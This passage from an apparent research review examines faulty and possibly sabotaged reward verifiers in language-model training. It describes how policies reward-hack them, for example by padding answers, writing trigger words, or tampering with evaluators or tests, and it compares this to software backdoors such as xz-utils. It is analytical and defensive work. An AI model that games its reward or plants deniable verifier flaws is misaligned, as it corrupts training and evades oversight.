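In experiments by Plesner and colleagues, noise did more harm when it flipped responses individually than when it flipped whole questions. At a 10% rate, the best score was 0.864 with individual flips, 0.891 with whole-question flips and 0.900 without noise, though they ran the individual version only twice. The effect of noise also varies by model. Gupta and Joshi report a mathematics experiment in which one model reached 72.0% with the rewards flipped on 40% of questions, against 75.9% without noise. Another model, Llama-3.1-8B, collapsed at 30%, where J is still 0.4 and the theory predicts only slower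 learning.

Plesner and colleagues resampled the noise each time the policy received a question. They point out that this doesn't represent a verifier with a persistent blind spot, which most bugs in reward code would produce.

### One rewarded word

Egashira and colleagues did test persistent blind spots. Their policies had to work out sums such as 332.419 − 993.538 + 740.756, so the researchers could check every answer exactly. They then added one error at a time to an otherwise perfect verifier. These are the shares of correct answers afterwards for two models:

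| Error in the verifier | Qwen3-1.7B | OLMo3-7B |
|---|---|---|
| None | 85.6% | 93.5% |
| Accepts half of all wrong answers at random | 82.2% | 87.4% |
| Accepts answers within 10% of the right one | 69.2% | 54.3% |
| Accepts any response containing "Certainly" | 64.3% | 54.3% |
| Accepts any response containing "python" | 0.6% | 2.0% |

Before training, the models got 20.6% and 16.2% right, so training with the "python" error made them far worse.

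The two words did different amounts of damage because they changed the rest of the answer in different ways. With "Certainly", the policy opened with the word and then mostly did the sum properly. But soon almost every response earned a reward, right or wrong, so the reward did little to improve the policy further. With "python", the policy learned to write something that looked like a program, followed by made-up program output.

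Egashira and colleagues measure this difference with "conditional advantage", the average advantage that responses containing a phrase would get from a perfect verifier. Suppose four of eight responses are right, so each right one has an advantage of +1 and each wrong one −1. If three responses contain the phrase and only one is right, rewarding the phrase would mostly reward wrong answers, and the conditional advantage is (1 − 1 − 1) / 3, or about −0.33.

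They then trained 51 models, each with a verifier that wrongly rewarded a different short phrase. Four of them show the pattern:

| Rewarded phrase | Responses containing it before training | Conditional advantage | Final accuracy |
|---|---|---|---|
| "to the result" | 12.1% | +0.27 | 68% |
| "add the first" | 5.1% | +0.21 | 72% |
| "reason step by" | 12.8% | −0.13 | 2% |
| "let me verify" | 5.9% | −0.14 | 89% |

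The first two phrases tend to appear in correct solutions, so accuracy rose and then stalled. "Reason step by" comes from the instructions, and that policy ended up repeating its instructions instead of answering. "Let me verify" also appeared in wrong answers, but it was rarer, and the policy learned to solve the sums without it.

Using a perfect verifier on every tenth training step largely fixed the stalled runs, but the collapsing run needed one on every second step. In most cases the policy kept producing the rewarded feature and combined it with correct reasoning.

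### The policy has to find the error

Training can only reinforce what the policy writes, so a word that the verifier would reward can't become more common if the policy never writes it. In the equations in *Rate or Fate?*, an answer that starts with a probability of zero likewise stays at zero.

Egashira and colleagues saw this happen with Qwen2.5-1.5B-Instruct, which had already been trained to follow instructions. It never wrote "python" during the run, so the error that ruined the other two models did not harm it. A laboratory could therefore use the same faulty reward code for years without trouble before it damaged a new model.

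The verifier also has to make an error reliably for training to collapse completely. When it made the "python" error only 80% of the time, training was much slower but no longer collapsed completely. At 50%, the policy didn't exploit the error and learned almost normally. A likely reason is that a correct answer always earned the reward, while a wrong answer containing the word earned it only half the time.

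The effect also depends on how many of the accepted answers are wrong when training begins. *Verifier Errors in RLVR* varied this share in a simplified simulation. At 10%, correctness improved. At 30%, it improved and then declined, and at 50% it declined from the start. Accepting wrong answers pushes the model to produce more of them, so a large enough share can become self-reinforcing.

The same paper gives an extreme example with a small language model. The task was to replace a series of digits according to given rules, but the verifier checked only the last two digits. Each question included a hint with those two digits right and the earlier ones wrong. Before reinforcement learning, the researchers trained the model on a mixture of examples, some of which copied the hint. After reinforcement learning, the verifier accepted 99.4% of the model's responses, but only 2.2% were correct.

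Policies also find faults that nobody planted. Gupta and Joshi describe a policy trained against a language-model judge that scored responses too highly because of their opening words. Eventually, 94% of the policy's outputs consisted only of "Thought Process:". With another judge, five of ten runs collapsed within about 170 steps, mostly into empty responses. Finding a fault can take longer. In an experiment with eight biases deliberately added to judges, policies exploited six after 68 to 478 steps and never exploited the other two.

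### Fewer errors, more damage

A verifier that wrongly accepts fewer answers can still do more harm to the model trained on it. Egashira and colleagues took a verifier that accepted answers slightly too high or too low and changed it to accept errors in only one direction. The new verifier wrongly accepted fewer answers at the start, but the policies trained on it ended up less accurate, especially OLMo3-7B. They suggest that the one-sided error pushed the policy to consistently overestimate or underestimate.

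The size of a tolerance can also matter. With Qwen2.5-1.5B-Instruct, a tolerance of 0.01% made accuracy stall, and every larger tolerance tested made it collapse. The off-by-one checker that Xin audited also had a 0.01% tolerance, although it judged different kinds of problems.

By contrast, a verifier that rejected anything written in English only delayed learning, even though it rejected nearly every right answer at first. Qwen3-1.7B learned to answer in Chinese, and OLMo3-7B fooled the language detector by repeating English words.

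*From Accuracy to Robustness* (2025) compared verifiers for mathematics and likewise concluded that a verifier's measured accuracy doesn't necessarily show how well it resists reward hacking, in which the policy raises its reward without doing the task better.

### Training against an exact score

Overall accuracy may be a poor guide to the damage, so in *Optimistic Verifiers Get Hacked*, Arunkumar and colleagues looked for another measure that might predict it before training begins. They needed a task where they could calculate the true quality of every response, so they used their rules for what an AI agent may do. Each situation the rules cover has ten features, such as the tool the agent would use and the user's role. The model has to explain a decision by naming the features that led to it.

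The exact score combines precision, the share of named features that really matter, with recall, the share of the necessary features that the model names:

F1 = 2 × precision × recall / (precision + recall)

It also subtracts penalties for excessive length and for stating the wrong decision. Late in one run, the model named eight features when only three determined the decision. If the eight included those three, recall was 1 and precision was 3/8, which gives an F1 of about 0.55. But one faulty verifier, the "sufficiency" verifier, checked only whether the named features were enough to settle the decision. They were, so the extra features did not lower the score from that verifier.

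The researchers built seven kinds of faulty verifier and audited them without using the model they planned to train. They wrote explanations of known quality and measured each verifier's selection error, which is how often it preferred the worse of two explanations, counting a tie as half. They also recorded whether each verifier was optimistic, scoring explanations too high on average, or pessimistic, scoring them too low.

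Then they trained a four-billion-parameter model for 150 steps with each verifier, while the exact score ran alongside without influencing the training. The model's true score was 0.731 at the start. Where the table gives two final scores, they come from two runs:

| Verifier | Selection error | True score after training |
|---|---|---|
| Exact | 0 | 0.838, 0.905 |
| Checks only the decision, not the reasons | 0.504 | 0.714 |
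| Checks only whether the named features settle the decision (sufficiency) | 0.208 | 0.667, 0.639 |
| Checks only recall | 0.132 | 0.692 |
| Misreads 5% of features at random | 0.043 | 0.821 |
| Misreads 15% of features at random | 0.143 | 0.678, 0.648 |
| Misreads 30% of features at random | 0.308 | 0.641 |
| Can't tell some related features apart | 0.030 | 0.844, 0.806 |
| Uses rules with one rule missing | 0.023–0.042 | 0.875, 0.840 |
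| Has a language model read the explanation | 0.090 | 0.865 |

(The last selection error comes from a separate audit on the training rules.)

In the first sufficiency run, the score from the faulty verifier reached 0.940 while the true score fell from 0.731 to 0.667. The policy had learned to pad its explanations, and the average number of features it named rose from 6.0 to 7.5.

The verifier that checked only the decision instead gave almost every response full marks from the start, so the policy had nothing to learn from in 137 of the 150 training steps.

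The last three verifiers did little or no harm. Their scores were sometimes far off, but they usually ranked better explanations above worse ones, and the training method relies mainly on that ranking. The researchers expected the policy to exploit the language-model judge because it scored the first responses too generously, but the judge proved safe, as the audit had suggested.

Random misreading at 15% did a lot of damage here, although Plesner and colleagues found little loss at 20%. The two percentages measure different things. The 15% is the chance of misreading each feature, so the verifier misreads at least one of the ten features in about 80% of explanations (1 − 0.85¹⁰).

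Arunkumar and colleagues summarised the damage, meaning the true score lost compared with exact training, in a formula:

damage ≈ β × selection error × share of steps with a usable signal

The estimated β was 1.81 for optimistic verifiers and 0.77 for pessimistic ones. If the selection error is 0.2 and half the steps have a usable signal, the formula gives a loss of about 0.18 for an optimistic verifier and 0.08 for a pessimistic one. An optimistic verifier rewards a bad habit that the policy can adopt, whereas a pessimistic one mostly wastes good responses. However, the formula was fitted after the first runs had finished, so its close match to those runs is weak evidence that it can predict new ones.

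### What did not replicate

The researchers rewrote the training program in another software framework and tried eight more configurations, some with a different model. The sufficiency verifier reduced the true score in all ten of its new runs, by more than two standard errors in seven of them. In all ten, the policy also named more features.

The size of the loss did not replicate. It averaged 0.218 in the original runs but ranged from 0.017 to 0.096 in the new ones. The estimates of β fell to about 0.57 and 0.18. Optimistic verifiers still did more damage for the same selection error, but the ratio could be anywhere from 1 to 10.5. The researchers tested several explanations, including numerical precision and the number of trained parameters, and none accounted for the difference.

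One of their predictions did hold. Phi-3.5-mini, the second model, lost only 0.017 at first. After more preliminary training raised its starting score from 0.672 to 0.764, the loss grew to 0.087. A more capable policy may therefore be better at exploiting the same fault.

The model also padded its answers on real access rules it hadn't seen, naming nearly every feature. It still got the highest overall score of all the models tested, because naming everything happens to score well on those rules. An evaluation that reported only the overall score would have ranked the damaged model first.

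The audit is promising for ranking verifiers by risk, but it can't yet predict how much damage to expect. It also requires examples of known quality, which the researchers had because they could calculate the right answer. They trained no model above four billion parameters, and several of the verifiers had only one run in the original set.

### Why other errors do little harm

Gupta and Joshi find that the type of error explains most of the apparent conflict between these results. Studies that report tolerance mostly used random errors, while collapse came from errors that the policy could trigger.

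Some systematic errors fall between the two because they affect only particular questions. In Zhang's programming experiment, weak tests raised the training reward by 8.37 points but changed the score on held-out tests by only 0.20. The wrong programs that earned rewards did not become more common over 800 steps. Wrong answer keys can do more harm. In one experiment that Gupta and Joshi describe, the wrong answers in the key were the model's own typical mistakes. Accuracy fell by 1.5 points when 10% of the answers were wrong and by 9.8 points when all were wrong.

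Li, Pandey and Chen (2026), in *Wrong the Same Way*, offer a possible explanation for why some errors grow and others don't. They trained a tiny model, with about 100,000 parameters, on 64 multiplication problems. For each problem, the verifier accepted the right answer and one wrong answer. They kept the number of errors constant and changed only how many problems had the same wrong answer accepted by the verifier.

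Before training, about 13% of the rewarded answers were wrong. When each problem had its own accepted wrong answer, that proportion fell to 2.5%. When all 64 problems had the same accepted wrong answer, the proportion ended at 16% on average, though individual runs ranged from 2% to 56%. At a higher learning rate, the proportion giving the shared wrong answer rose in all ten runs, by an average of 60 percentage points.

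The model uses the same parameters for every problem, so when the verifier accepts a wrong answer on one problem, the model becomes more likely to give that answer on others, and less likely when the verifier rejects it. When Li and colleagues gave every problem its own copy of the model, the effect disappeared. This might explain why Zhang's weak tests, which accept different wrong programs for different tasks, did so little damage, while a word that earns a reward on every question can ruin a model.

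Li and colleagues also compared two ways of repairing a verifier. One removed a wrong answer that the verifier accepted on every problem, and the other removed the same number of scattered errors. The first led to 98.7% accuracy and the second to 90.9%. At the higher learning rate, the gap averaged 38 points. The verifier's own reward was at least 0.973 in every case, so nobody could have told from it which repair had worked. They haven't tested their explanation on full-size language models, and their results depended heavily on the learning rate.

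### Errors injected in the open

Researchers have also studied deliberately poisoned RLVR data, as in *Backdoors in RLVR* (2026). In the controlled studies of verifier errors, by contrast, Egashira, Arunkumar, Li and their colleagues introduced the errors openly to measure their effect on the policy. None of them gave the faulty code to an unsuspecting reviewer, as the Minnesota researchers did with their kernel patches, so their results can't show how likely a reviewer is to notice such an error.

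The amount of damage a flaw does doesn't show how easily its author could pass it off as innocent. A rule that accepts any response containing "python" would look strange to anyone who read it, and its author would struggle to call it a mistake. The numerical tolerance did less damage in the main experiments, but it could pass for an ordinary choice, like the one in Xin's off-by-one checker.

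## Which lessons carry over to reward code?

Most lessons from the Linux, Minnesota and xz-utils cases apply to reward code, because people write, review and repair it much as they do other software. The cases show what reviewers read closely, what they take on trust and how a flaw comes to light. This is some of the evidence missing from research on faulty verifiers, where researchers inserted faults but never had to hide them from a colleague. The comparison is weaker for what happens once the code is in use.

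### Small changes, repairs and unread data

A reviewer can't judge the risk of a code change by its length. One missing equals sign would have given users of an affected Linux machine full control of it, and one stray dot kept a protection out of every xz-utils build that used the altered check. Reward code can be just as sensitive to small details. The checker that Xin audited had a tolerance of 0.0001, which made it accept every off-by-one answer when the reference was 10,000 or more.

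But a small flaw in a verifier may also have no effect. Rewarding the word "python" ruined two of the models that Egashira and colleagues trained, but a third was unharmed because it never wrote the word. The 2003 backdoor, by contrast, would have worked the same way on every machine that ran it.

The Minnesota researchers and Jia Tan both presented harmful changes as repairs. Reward code constantly needs repairs, such as loosening a checker that rejects right answers or adding stricter tests when wrong programs pass. Either change can go too far without anyone intending it. When Rajan had a language model write stricter tests, for example, most of the tests that gave a clear result failed on the correct solution.

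Latent Space's *How to Stop Shipping Low-Quality RL Environments (with Examples)* lists other faults that people introduce by accident. The software may not reset fully between attempts, so the policy can gain or lose reward for something left over from the previous attempt. It may also round scores so that an excellent answer and a mediocre one both earn 1, so the policy learns nothing from the difference. A colleague who found either fault would have good reason to assume it was a careless mistake.

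Test data matters more in reward code than it did in xz-utils. Jia Tan's test files did nothing until a build script extracted the payload from them, whereas a wrong entry in an answer key changes the reward directly. Wrong entries can remain even where anyone can read them, as the wrong reference solutions in HumanEval did. But they are easier to check than the xz-utils files, because anyone who can solve a problem can compare their solution with the key.

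The lesson about trust probably carries over too. Torvalds relies on the people who send him patches, and Jia Tan could merge the payload without anyone else's approval. An employee who writes training tasks is in a similar position to Jia Tan, because colleagues already know them and expect their code. Redwood Research suspected that nobody at Anthropic was responsible for checking what the reward code received, and an honest mistake there went unnoticed for a long time.

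### Outside suppliers and shared collections

Laboratories don't write all their reward code themselves. Some can come as part of an environment, which contains a task, the software through which the model acts, and the grading rules. The company Prime Intellect has a shared collection of environments. Sequoia Capital's *Building the GitHub for RL Environments*, which features two people from the company, compares building environments to the earlier work of labelling data by hand.

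Fehler (2026) writes in *RL environments for agentic AI* that in 2025 Anthropic planned to spend more than $1 billion on RL environments over the following year, and that OpenAI signed several seven-figure contracts. These figures need some caution because the article appeared on the website of Prolific, a vendor with a commercial interest in the market.

Epoch AI interviewed people about environments in early 2026. Mathematics and coding tasks came first, but demand was growing for office work such as filing reports and editing spreadsheets. Interviewees consistently named resistance to reward hacking as a mark of quality, which took many rounds of revision to achieve. They found it hard to coordinate a growing number of task builders and still check everyone's work properly.

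AI Engineer summarises a 2026 conference talk that describes a similar problem. Researchers review sets of tasks with experts, and sometimes with data vendors, but this review becomes harder to scale when users may ask a model for almost anything.

Trying to exploit an environment before using it can uncover deliberate flaws as well as accidental ones. This doesn't show who wrote each line, or whether someone altered the package before it reached the customer. A laboratory that trains on a supplier's environment also depends on the supplier's staff and machines, much as Debian's users depended on xz-utils without choosing it.

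A supplier's security can fail even if all its developers are honest. Kokkonis and colleagues describe how, in 2021, intruders broke into the server that held the source code of PHP, a programming language for websites, and added a backdoor. The backdoor never reached an official release, but anyone who copied the source code while it was there would have received it.

Sharing also spreads honest mistakes, because one flaw in a checker that many laboratories use can affect all their models. But having more users can also make it more likely that an outsider like Freund will notice something wrong.

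### A flaw that works without its author

A software backdoor has no effect until somebody uses it, whereas an exploitable false positive in a verifier starts to affect the policy once the policy happens to write an answer that triggers it, even if the author has left. The false positive also gives its author no access to anything. A trained model can also contain the more familiar kind of backdoor, and *Backdoors in RLVR* reports a laboratory demonstration that planted one through the training data without changing the verifier.

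The maker of a software backdoor can test it before releasing it. Jia Tan could have installed the same version of Debian as the intended victims and checked whether the backdoor worked. Someone planting a flaw in a verifier would instead have to predict how a particular policy would behave over a whole training run.

Gupta and Joshi list several experiments that show how difficult this would be. In one, the policy could overwrite the tests that scored it, but it learned to do so in only two of eight cases that used reinforcement learning alone. In another, the policy's early attempts to tamper with the evaluator failed and became rarer, but later attempts succeeded. By the end, 99.9% of its responses exploited the evaluator, and it solved only 1.2% of the problems.

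A verifier's error rate can also change when nobody edits the code. Gupta and Joshi cite a verifier that judged answers without an answer key. It accepted 32% of wrong answers from a weak model but 83% of those from a stronger one. A saboteur would struggle to plan around such a change, as would a laboratory that had measured the verifier only once, before training.

An exploited flaw also leaves more evidence than an unused backdoor. Freund could observe only side effects, such as a half-second delay. When a policy exploits a verifier, the habit appears in its answers, sometimes in nearly all of them, and anyone who reads a sample may notice it. Some habits are harder to notice, such as those of the policies that Arunkumar and colleagues trained with the sufficiency verifier, which named a few more features than they needed to.

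A model is harder to repair than ordinary software. Users could remove the xz-utils backdoor from their machines by installing the clean version Collin released. Correcting a verifier changes only its future rewards. The model keeps what it has already learned, so its developers have to train it further or go back to a copy saved before the fault took effect.

Developers may also have to find out where else the fault has spread. Sequoia Capital notes that they can use the same environment to generate training data, or for distillation, in which one model learns from another's answers. Rajan found wrong patches in public training collections whose creators had kept only patches that passed the tests. Better tests would not remove those patches from existing copies of the collections, or undo their effect on models already trained on them.

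Private reward code also has fewer potential readers. Readers of the kernel mailing list recognised the 2003 backdoor 25 minutes after McVoy posted the lines, and Freund could compare the xz-utils tarball with a public repository. Outsiders can't check a private verifier in either way, so the laboratory's staff have to find the problem or bring in someone who can.

Some backdoor detectors would miss a wrong verdict. Kokkonis and colleagues built one that watches a program's system calls, the requests it makes to the operating system, such as opening a file. It raises an alarm when a new version makes an unusual combination of calls that the old version did not make on the same input. They assume that any meaningful backdoor in a program's code has to make system calls, because a program needs them to affect anything outside itself.

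That is reasonable for a backdoor that opens a command line. But Xin's off-by-one checker needs no extra system call to accept 10,001 when the key has 10,000. It reads the answer, does some arithmetic and returns a verdict, as it does for a correct answer. A tool that looks for extra system calls might be more likely to detect a program that overwrites its own tests, since that requires writing to a file.

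### Has anyone documented a poisoned verifier?

As of 5 December 2026, none of the studies and news reports consulted here documents a deliberately poisoned verifier in a real training run. Gupta and Joshi compare 16 studies of training with faulty verifiers or with checkers that the policy could alter. Some faults were part of the experiment and others were accidental, but none was sabotage against an unsuspecting developer.

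An obscure case could still exist, because any record of a poisoned verifier that passed for an honest mistake would describe it as a bug. But the same argument could explain the lack of evidence for almost any hidden attack, so it gives no reason to think that poisoned verifiers are common.

### The ByteDance intern

The closest case found concerns the software that ran training jobs, not a verifier. In October 2024, posts on Chinese social media alleged that an intern had sabotaged AI training at ByteDance, TikTok's parent company. According to the rumours, the attack affected more than 8,000 processors and cost over $10 million.

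Fortune (2024) reported that ByteDance confirmed it had dismissed an intern who "maliciously interfered" with model training. ByteDance called the rumoured figures greatly exaggerated, according to *被字节辞退实习生AI创业融资近3000万美元，叫板“AI教母”？* (2026) from the Chinese news service 凤凰网科技.

An internal notice of 5 November 2024 accused a former intern surnamed Tian of writing and altering code in June and July to attack a research project's training jobs, out of dissatisfaction with how the team allocated resources. 凤凰网科技's *被字节开除的实习生、北大博士田柯宇，在世界模型领域创业* (2026) describes the notice and, citing people inside the company, says Tian had denied responsibility and blamed other interns.

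ByteDance then sued Tian Keyu for 8 million yuan (about $1.1 million) in damages and demanded a public apology. TechNode's *ByteDance sues former intern for alleged code tampering* (2024) reports the company's claim that the interference had affected a research project but no official projects or other business. The first court ordered Tian to pay 500,000 yuan for breach of contract and rejected the claims for 8 million yuan and an apology. ByteDance's appeal was still pending in October 2026, according to 凤凰网科技's *被字节开除实习生田柯宇创业估值2亿美元 投毒事件双方说法分歧* (2026).

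Tian gave a fuller account in a podcast that month. He admitted using a program, written with an AI model's help, to stop or freeze another intern's jobs. He said he had done this by hand about five times in roughly ten days, because the other intern kept stopping colleagues' jobs and the team's leaders had not solved the problem. He denied wanting the computing power for himself.

Former colleagues soon published a very different account, which five of them signed by name. They allege that the sabotage lasted from March to July 2024 and that Tian disguised it as random faults, as 虎嗅网's *田柯宇发誓，说谎会“终生研究受挫”* (2026) reports. By their account, it affected a small research project and then a larger one building a video-generation model.

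The faults came and went, so the team couldn't easily tell whether the hardware, data, settings or code caused them. When a job recovered after a change, they couldn't be sure the change had fixed it. They also say Tian attended meetings about the faults.

According to the same statement, someone investigating a faulty job on 30 July happened to notice altered code on a machine that only Tian and its owner had logged in to. The next day the team found more suspicious code in Tian's personal folder. 凤凰网科技 found evidence that three of the signatories had worked at ByteDance, which makes them credible witnesses but doesn't confirm each allegation. Neither Tian nor ByteDance had responded to the new claims when the article appeared.

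Even by Tian's account, an insider deliberately interfered with a colleague's training jobs. If his former colleagues are right, the case also resembles the xz-utils backdoor, because a trusted team member joined discussions of problems he had caused.

| Case | Who made the change | Innocent explanation | How it came to light |
|---|---|---|---|
| Linux, 2003 | An intruder | A typing error in an error check | A nightly comparison with the original |
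| Minnesota, 2020 | Outside contributors | Mistakes in small repairs | The researchers' own announcement |
| xz-utils, 2024 | A trusted maintainer | None for the payload, but several for the changes around it | Slow logins and memory errors |
| ByteDance, 2024 | An intern on the team | Chance faults in training, according to former colleagues | Altered code that someone happened to notice, according to former colleagues |

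### Are a laboratory's own controls enough?

A sceptic could argue that open-source projects are a poor guide to AI laboratories, which control their staff. Nobody has identified Jia Tan, but a laboratory knows whom it employs, can record who used each machine and can take an offender to court. In Beijing's first criminal case over damage to an AI model, a court sentenced an engineer surnamed Wang to five years and ten months in prison, according to 每日经济新闻's *北京首例破坏AI模型刑案落槌* (2026).

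Laboratories also test their models separately from training, and serious damage should be obvious. The damage sometimes extends to unrelated skills. Gupta and Joshi cite an experiment in which a small model's score on ARC-C, a set of science questions, fell from 73.9 to 43.9 after training with a noisy verifier.

People write the tests and formal statements used in RLVR, and they can get both wrong. This weakens the claim, which Gupta and Joshi attribute to an earlier survey, that RLVR effectively eliminates reward hacking because a policy can't trick a compiler or a proof checker.

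A laboratory's control over its staff is an advantage, but much of that advantage depends on somebody becoming suspicious. In the former colleagues' account of the ByteDance case, faults went unexplained for months before someone found the altered code, and the login records then quickly pointed to Tian. A laboratory also has less control over a supplier's employees or over contributors to a shared collection. Wang's offence was deletion, which is much harder to pass off as a mistake than a badly chosen tolerance.

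A poisoned verifier gives the saboteur no access, and its effects are hard to predict, so a spy who wants to get into particular machines would find a backdoor like the one in xz-utils far more useful. But someone with a grudge may not need a predictable result. ByteDance blamed Tian's actions on resentment over resources, and Tian says he was angry with another intern.

The sceptic's better argument is separate testing, but it holds only if the tests are separate. Sequoia Capital notes that developers can use the same environment for training and evaluation. An environment that wrongly rewards an answer could then raise the model's score in both. Adding more language models as judges may help less than expected, because their mistakes overlap. Gupta and Joshi cite a study in which nine leading judges were worth only about two independent votes.

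A good independent test would probably catch a collapse, but a moderate loss is harder to recognise because the model may still have improved. When a verifier wrongly rewarded the word "Certainly", one of Egashira's models still became about three times as accurate as before training. The researchers could measure the loss because they had also trained the model with a perfect verifier, but a laboratory without that second run would have seen only the improvement.

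## Can sabotage be told from a mistake?

Suppose someone at a laboratory finds a line in a verifier that looks wrong. The staff then have to work out whether the code is wrong, whether the error serves anyone, and whether its author intended it. It's easy to take an answer to one of the first two questions as an answer to the third, but they need different evidence. This is how people answered them in the open-source cases:

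| Flaw | Is the code wrong? | Whom could it serve? | Did the author intend it? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Linux, 2003 | Yes, developers read the two lines | Any user of an affected machine who knew of it | Yes, an intruder added it under another developer's name |
| Minnesota, flawed patches of 2020 | Yes, a reviewer recognised one flaw and the researchers disclosed the others | An attacker, if maintainers had merged them | Yes, the researchers said so |
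| Minnesota, Pakki's patches of April 2021 | Reviewers rejected them as poor | Nobody obvious | No, according to the university |
| xz-utils, the payload | Yes, Freund traced slow logins to it | Only the holder of a secret key | Yes, nobody writes such a key check by accident |
| xz-utils, the stray dot | Yes, it stopped a test program from compiling | Hard to say | Unsettled, since the main evidence is that Jia Tan wrote it |

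Reading and running the code was enough to answer the first question. It answered the third only for the xz-utils payload, which could not have passed for a mistake. For the other flaws, people relied on a confession, a university's statement, evidence of a break-in or what they knew about the author.

### Who benefits?

*Surreptitiously Weakening Cryptographic Systems* (Schneier, Fredrikson and colleagues, 2015) defines "control" as how far a saboteur can limit who exploits a weakness, even after it becomes public. Its example of high control is Dual EC, a random number generator that the US standards agency NIST adopted. Whoever chose certain constants in the generator could keep a secret that let them predict its output, and nobody else could realistically work out that secret. The National Security Agency (NSA) allegedly did this.

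If only the attacker can exploit a flaw, that is good evidence of intent. The xz-utils payload, for example, checked for the attacker's key. The absence of such a restriction is poor evidence of innocence, since the 2003 Linux backdoor was deliberate even though any local user could have exploited it.

Asking who benefits from a flaw is less helpful for reward code. A false positive raises the training score, so it benefits anyone whose manager judges them by that score, even if they don't know about the flaw. Someone who sabotages the code out of a grudge may gain nothing except the damage.

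### A contest for innocent-looking flaws

In the Underhanded C Contest, founded by the engineering professor Scott Craver, programmers compete to write short, readable code that looks innocent but does something malicious. Past challenges have included miscounting votes, taking money from financial transactions and leaking information.

The 2015 contest, run in partnership with the non-profit Nuclear Threat Initiative (NTI), used a task from nuclear arms control. Entrants wrote a simple warhead-checking program that an adversary could fool. The winning entry was in effect a verifier with a deliberate false positive, and Craver said it showed how an inspector might mistake a fake warhead for a real one.

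The Underhanded C Contest judged entries partly on "plausible deniability of the intended error", according to NTI's *“Underhanded C” Contest Highlights Challenges For Nuclear Arms Control Verification Technologies*. The judges knew that every entry was malicious, so the contest can't show how many reviewers an entry would fool. But it does show that a skilled programmer can write a flaw with an excuse that readers find believable even when they know the flaw is deliberate. NTI added that there were no standards for writing or reviewing code for arms control inspections.

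### How much does finding a flaw prove?

Bayes' rule is a formula for updating a probability given new evidence. Here it requires three figures: how common sabotage is, how likely the evidence is if there was sabotage, and how likely it is if there wasn't. Nobody knows these figures for verifiers, so those below are only illustrative.

Suppose saboteurs have tampered with 1 verifier in 1,000, and every sabotaged verifier has an exploitable flaw. Suppose 28.5% of honest verifiers have one too, which is the rate Gupta and Joshi cite for a set of coding tasks. An investigator then finds such a flaw. The probability of sabotage is

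(1 × 0.001) / (1 × 0.001 + 0.285 × 0.999) ≈ 0.0035, or 0.35%

If 100 of 100,000 verifiers are sabotaged, all 100 will have a flaw, but so will about 28,470 of the 99,900 honest ones. Only 100 of the roughly 28,570 flawed verifiers are therefore sabotaged. Finding the flaw raises the probability of sabotage from 0.1% to 0.35%, but an investigator who accused every author of a flawed verifier would be wrong more than 99% of the time.

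Suppose the investigator also finds what looks like a forged approval, and that this is 100 times more likely in a sabotage case than in an honest one. For example, half of all saboteurs might forge an approval, while one honest case in 200 might contain something that looks like a forgery. That leaves 50 sabotaged verifiers and about 142 honest ones, so the probability of sabotage rises to 50 / 192, or about 26%, and most of these authors would still be innocent.

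Finding no forgery would change the probability much less, from 0.35% to about 0.18%, because half of the saboteurs in this example don't forge anything.

The results depend heavily on the assumptions:

| Assumption changed | Chance of sabotage after finding the flaw | After also finding the forged approval |
|---|---|---|
| None | 0.35% | 26% |
| 22.4% of honest verifiers have a flaw | 0.44% | 31% |
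| 57.8% of honest verifiers have a flaw | 0.17% | 15% |
| Saboteurs have tampered with 1 verifier in 100 | 3.4% | 78% |
| Saboteurs have tampered with 1 in 10,000 | 0.035% | 3.4% |

Rajan's corrected rate is 22.4%, and the rate with a stronger attacking model is 57.8%. As people get better at finding honest flaws, each flaw they find is weaker evidence of sabotage. The share of verifiers that are sabotaged has the largest effect on the probability that a flaw is sabotage, and investigators know least about that share because nobody has documented a case.

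The second step also assumes that the forged approval is independent of the evidence already counted. Suppose the investigator also finds a false name. Anyone who forges an approval probably has to use one, and if the two clues always occur together, the false name adds no evidence and the probability stays at 26%. Treating it as another independent clue, 100 times more likely under sabotage, would wrongly raise the probability to 97%.

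### Clues in the code

A change that doesn't fit its stated purpose is suspicious. A commenter on Freedom to Tinker read the 2003 Linux lines as their author supposedly meant them, with two equals signs instead of one. The code would then have rejected a harmless combination of settings, and only when the administrator sent it. The commenter couldn't see why anyone would want that. The mismatch could still be innocent if the programmer misunderstood the settings. A good fit is also weak evidence of innocence, since the Minnesota researchers gave their flawed patches believable purposes.

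Investigators may also look at how precise the trigger is, but a rare trigger doesn't rule out a mistake. A backdoor usually needs a rare condition so that it stays inactive in ordinary use. Bugs that survive for years also tend to need rare conditions, because people quickly notice bugs that affect everybody. The off-by-one checker that Xin audited failed only when the reference answer was 10,000 or more, and nobody has suggested that the error was deliberate.

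Language models also write suspiciously precise code. In the training data Rajan examined, one patch recognised the random numbers used in a test and returned answers from a prepared table. Another made an exception for the exact case the test checked. A reviewer who found either in a colleague's work might well suspect bad faith, but a model wrote both to pass the tests.

### Clues in the record

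The 2021 backdoor in PHP came with several clues outside the code. Shree notes in *Can You Trust the Commit?* that the attacker impersonated someone else, described the change as a typo fix and submitted it at 06:00, although the previous 20 commits had all come after 18:00.

Shree writes, "Anomaly is not maliciousness." Honest developers sometimes work at strange hours or use pseudonyms. Collin's notes on Tukaani mention ordinary Git commands that change a commit's recorded date, as well as commits made in another person's name with permission. Using a real colleague's name without permission is much harder to explain innocently.

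A missing approval can also be innocent, as when a tired developer skips review to meet a deadline. It is weaker evidence of sabotage in projects where honest developers often skip review. In Nealon's data, about 2% of contributors had merged their own changes without review. If 2% of honest contributors do this, a saboteur is at most 50 times as likely to do it (1 / 0.02), even if every saboteur does.

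Jia Tan's work showed that a valid approval doesn't prove that a contributor is acting in good faith. In a test of one commit-scanning tool that Shree describes, all seven malicious commits the tool missed came from trusted contributors.

### Repeated errors and suspicious answers

Several errors in the same direction can look deliberate. Suppose someone has written verifiers with ten known flaws, and all ten reward wrong answers. If honest errors were equally likely to reward wrong answers or penalize right ones, the chance of this would be 1 in 1,024.

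But honest errors in verifiers are rarely so balanced. Gupta and Joshi report that when rule-based checkers accept a mathematics answer, it is right at least 99% of the time, but they reject between 7% and 14% of right answers on average. Test suites tend to make the opposite error and accept wrong programs. If 95% of the honest errors in a type of verifier reward wrong answers, the chance that ten out of ten honest errors do so is about 60%.

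The total number of verifiers a person has written also matters, because at the 28.5% rate, someone who honestly wrote 100 would have about 28 with an exploitable flaw.

People's behavior when challenged can be revealing, but it is easy to misread. Freund cited Jia Tan's mailing-list discussions of the supposed fixes. These were good evidence that the account's real owner was responsible, since an intruder would have had to carry on the discussions without the owner noticing. They would have been weaker evidence of intent, because an honest maintainer discusses fixes too.

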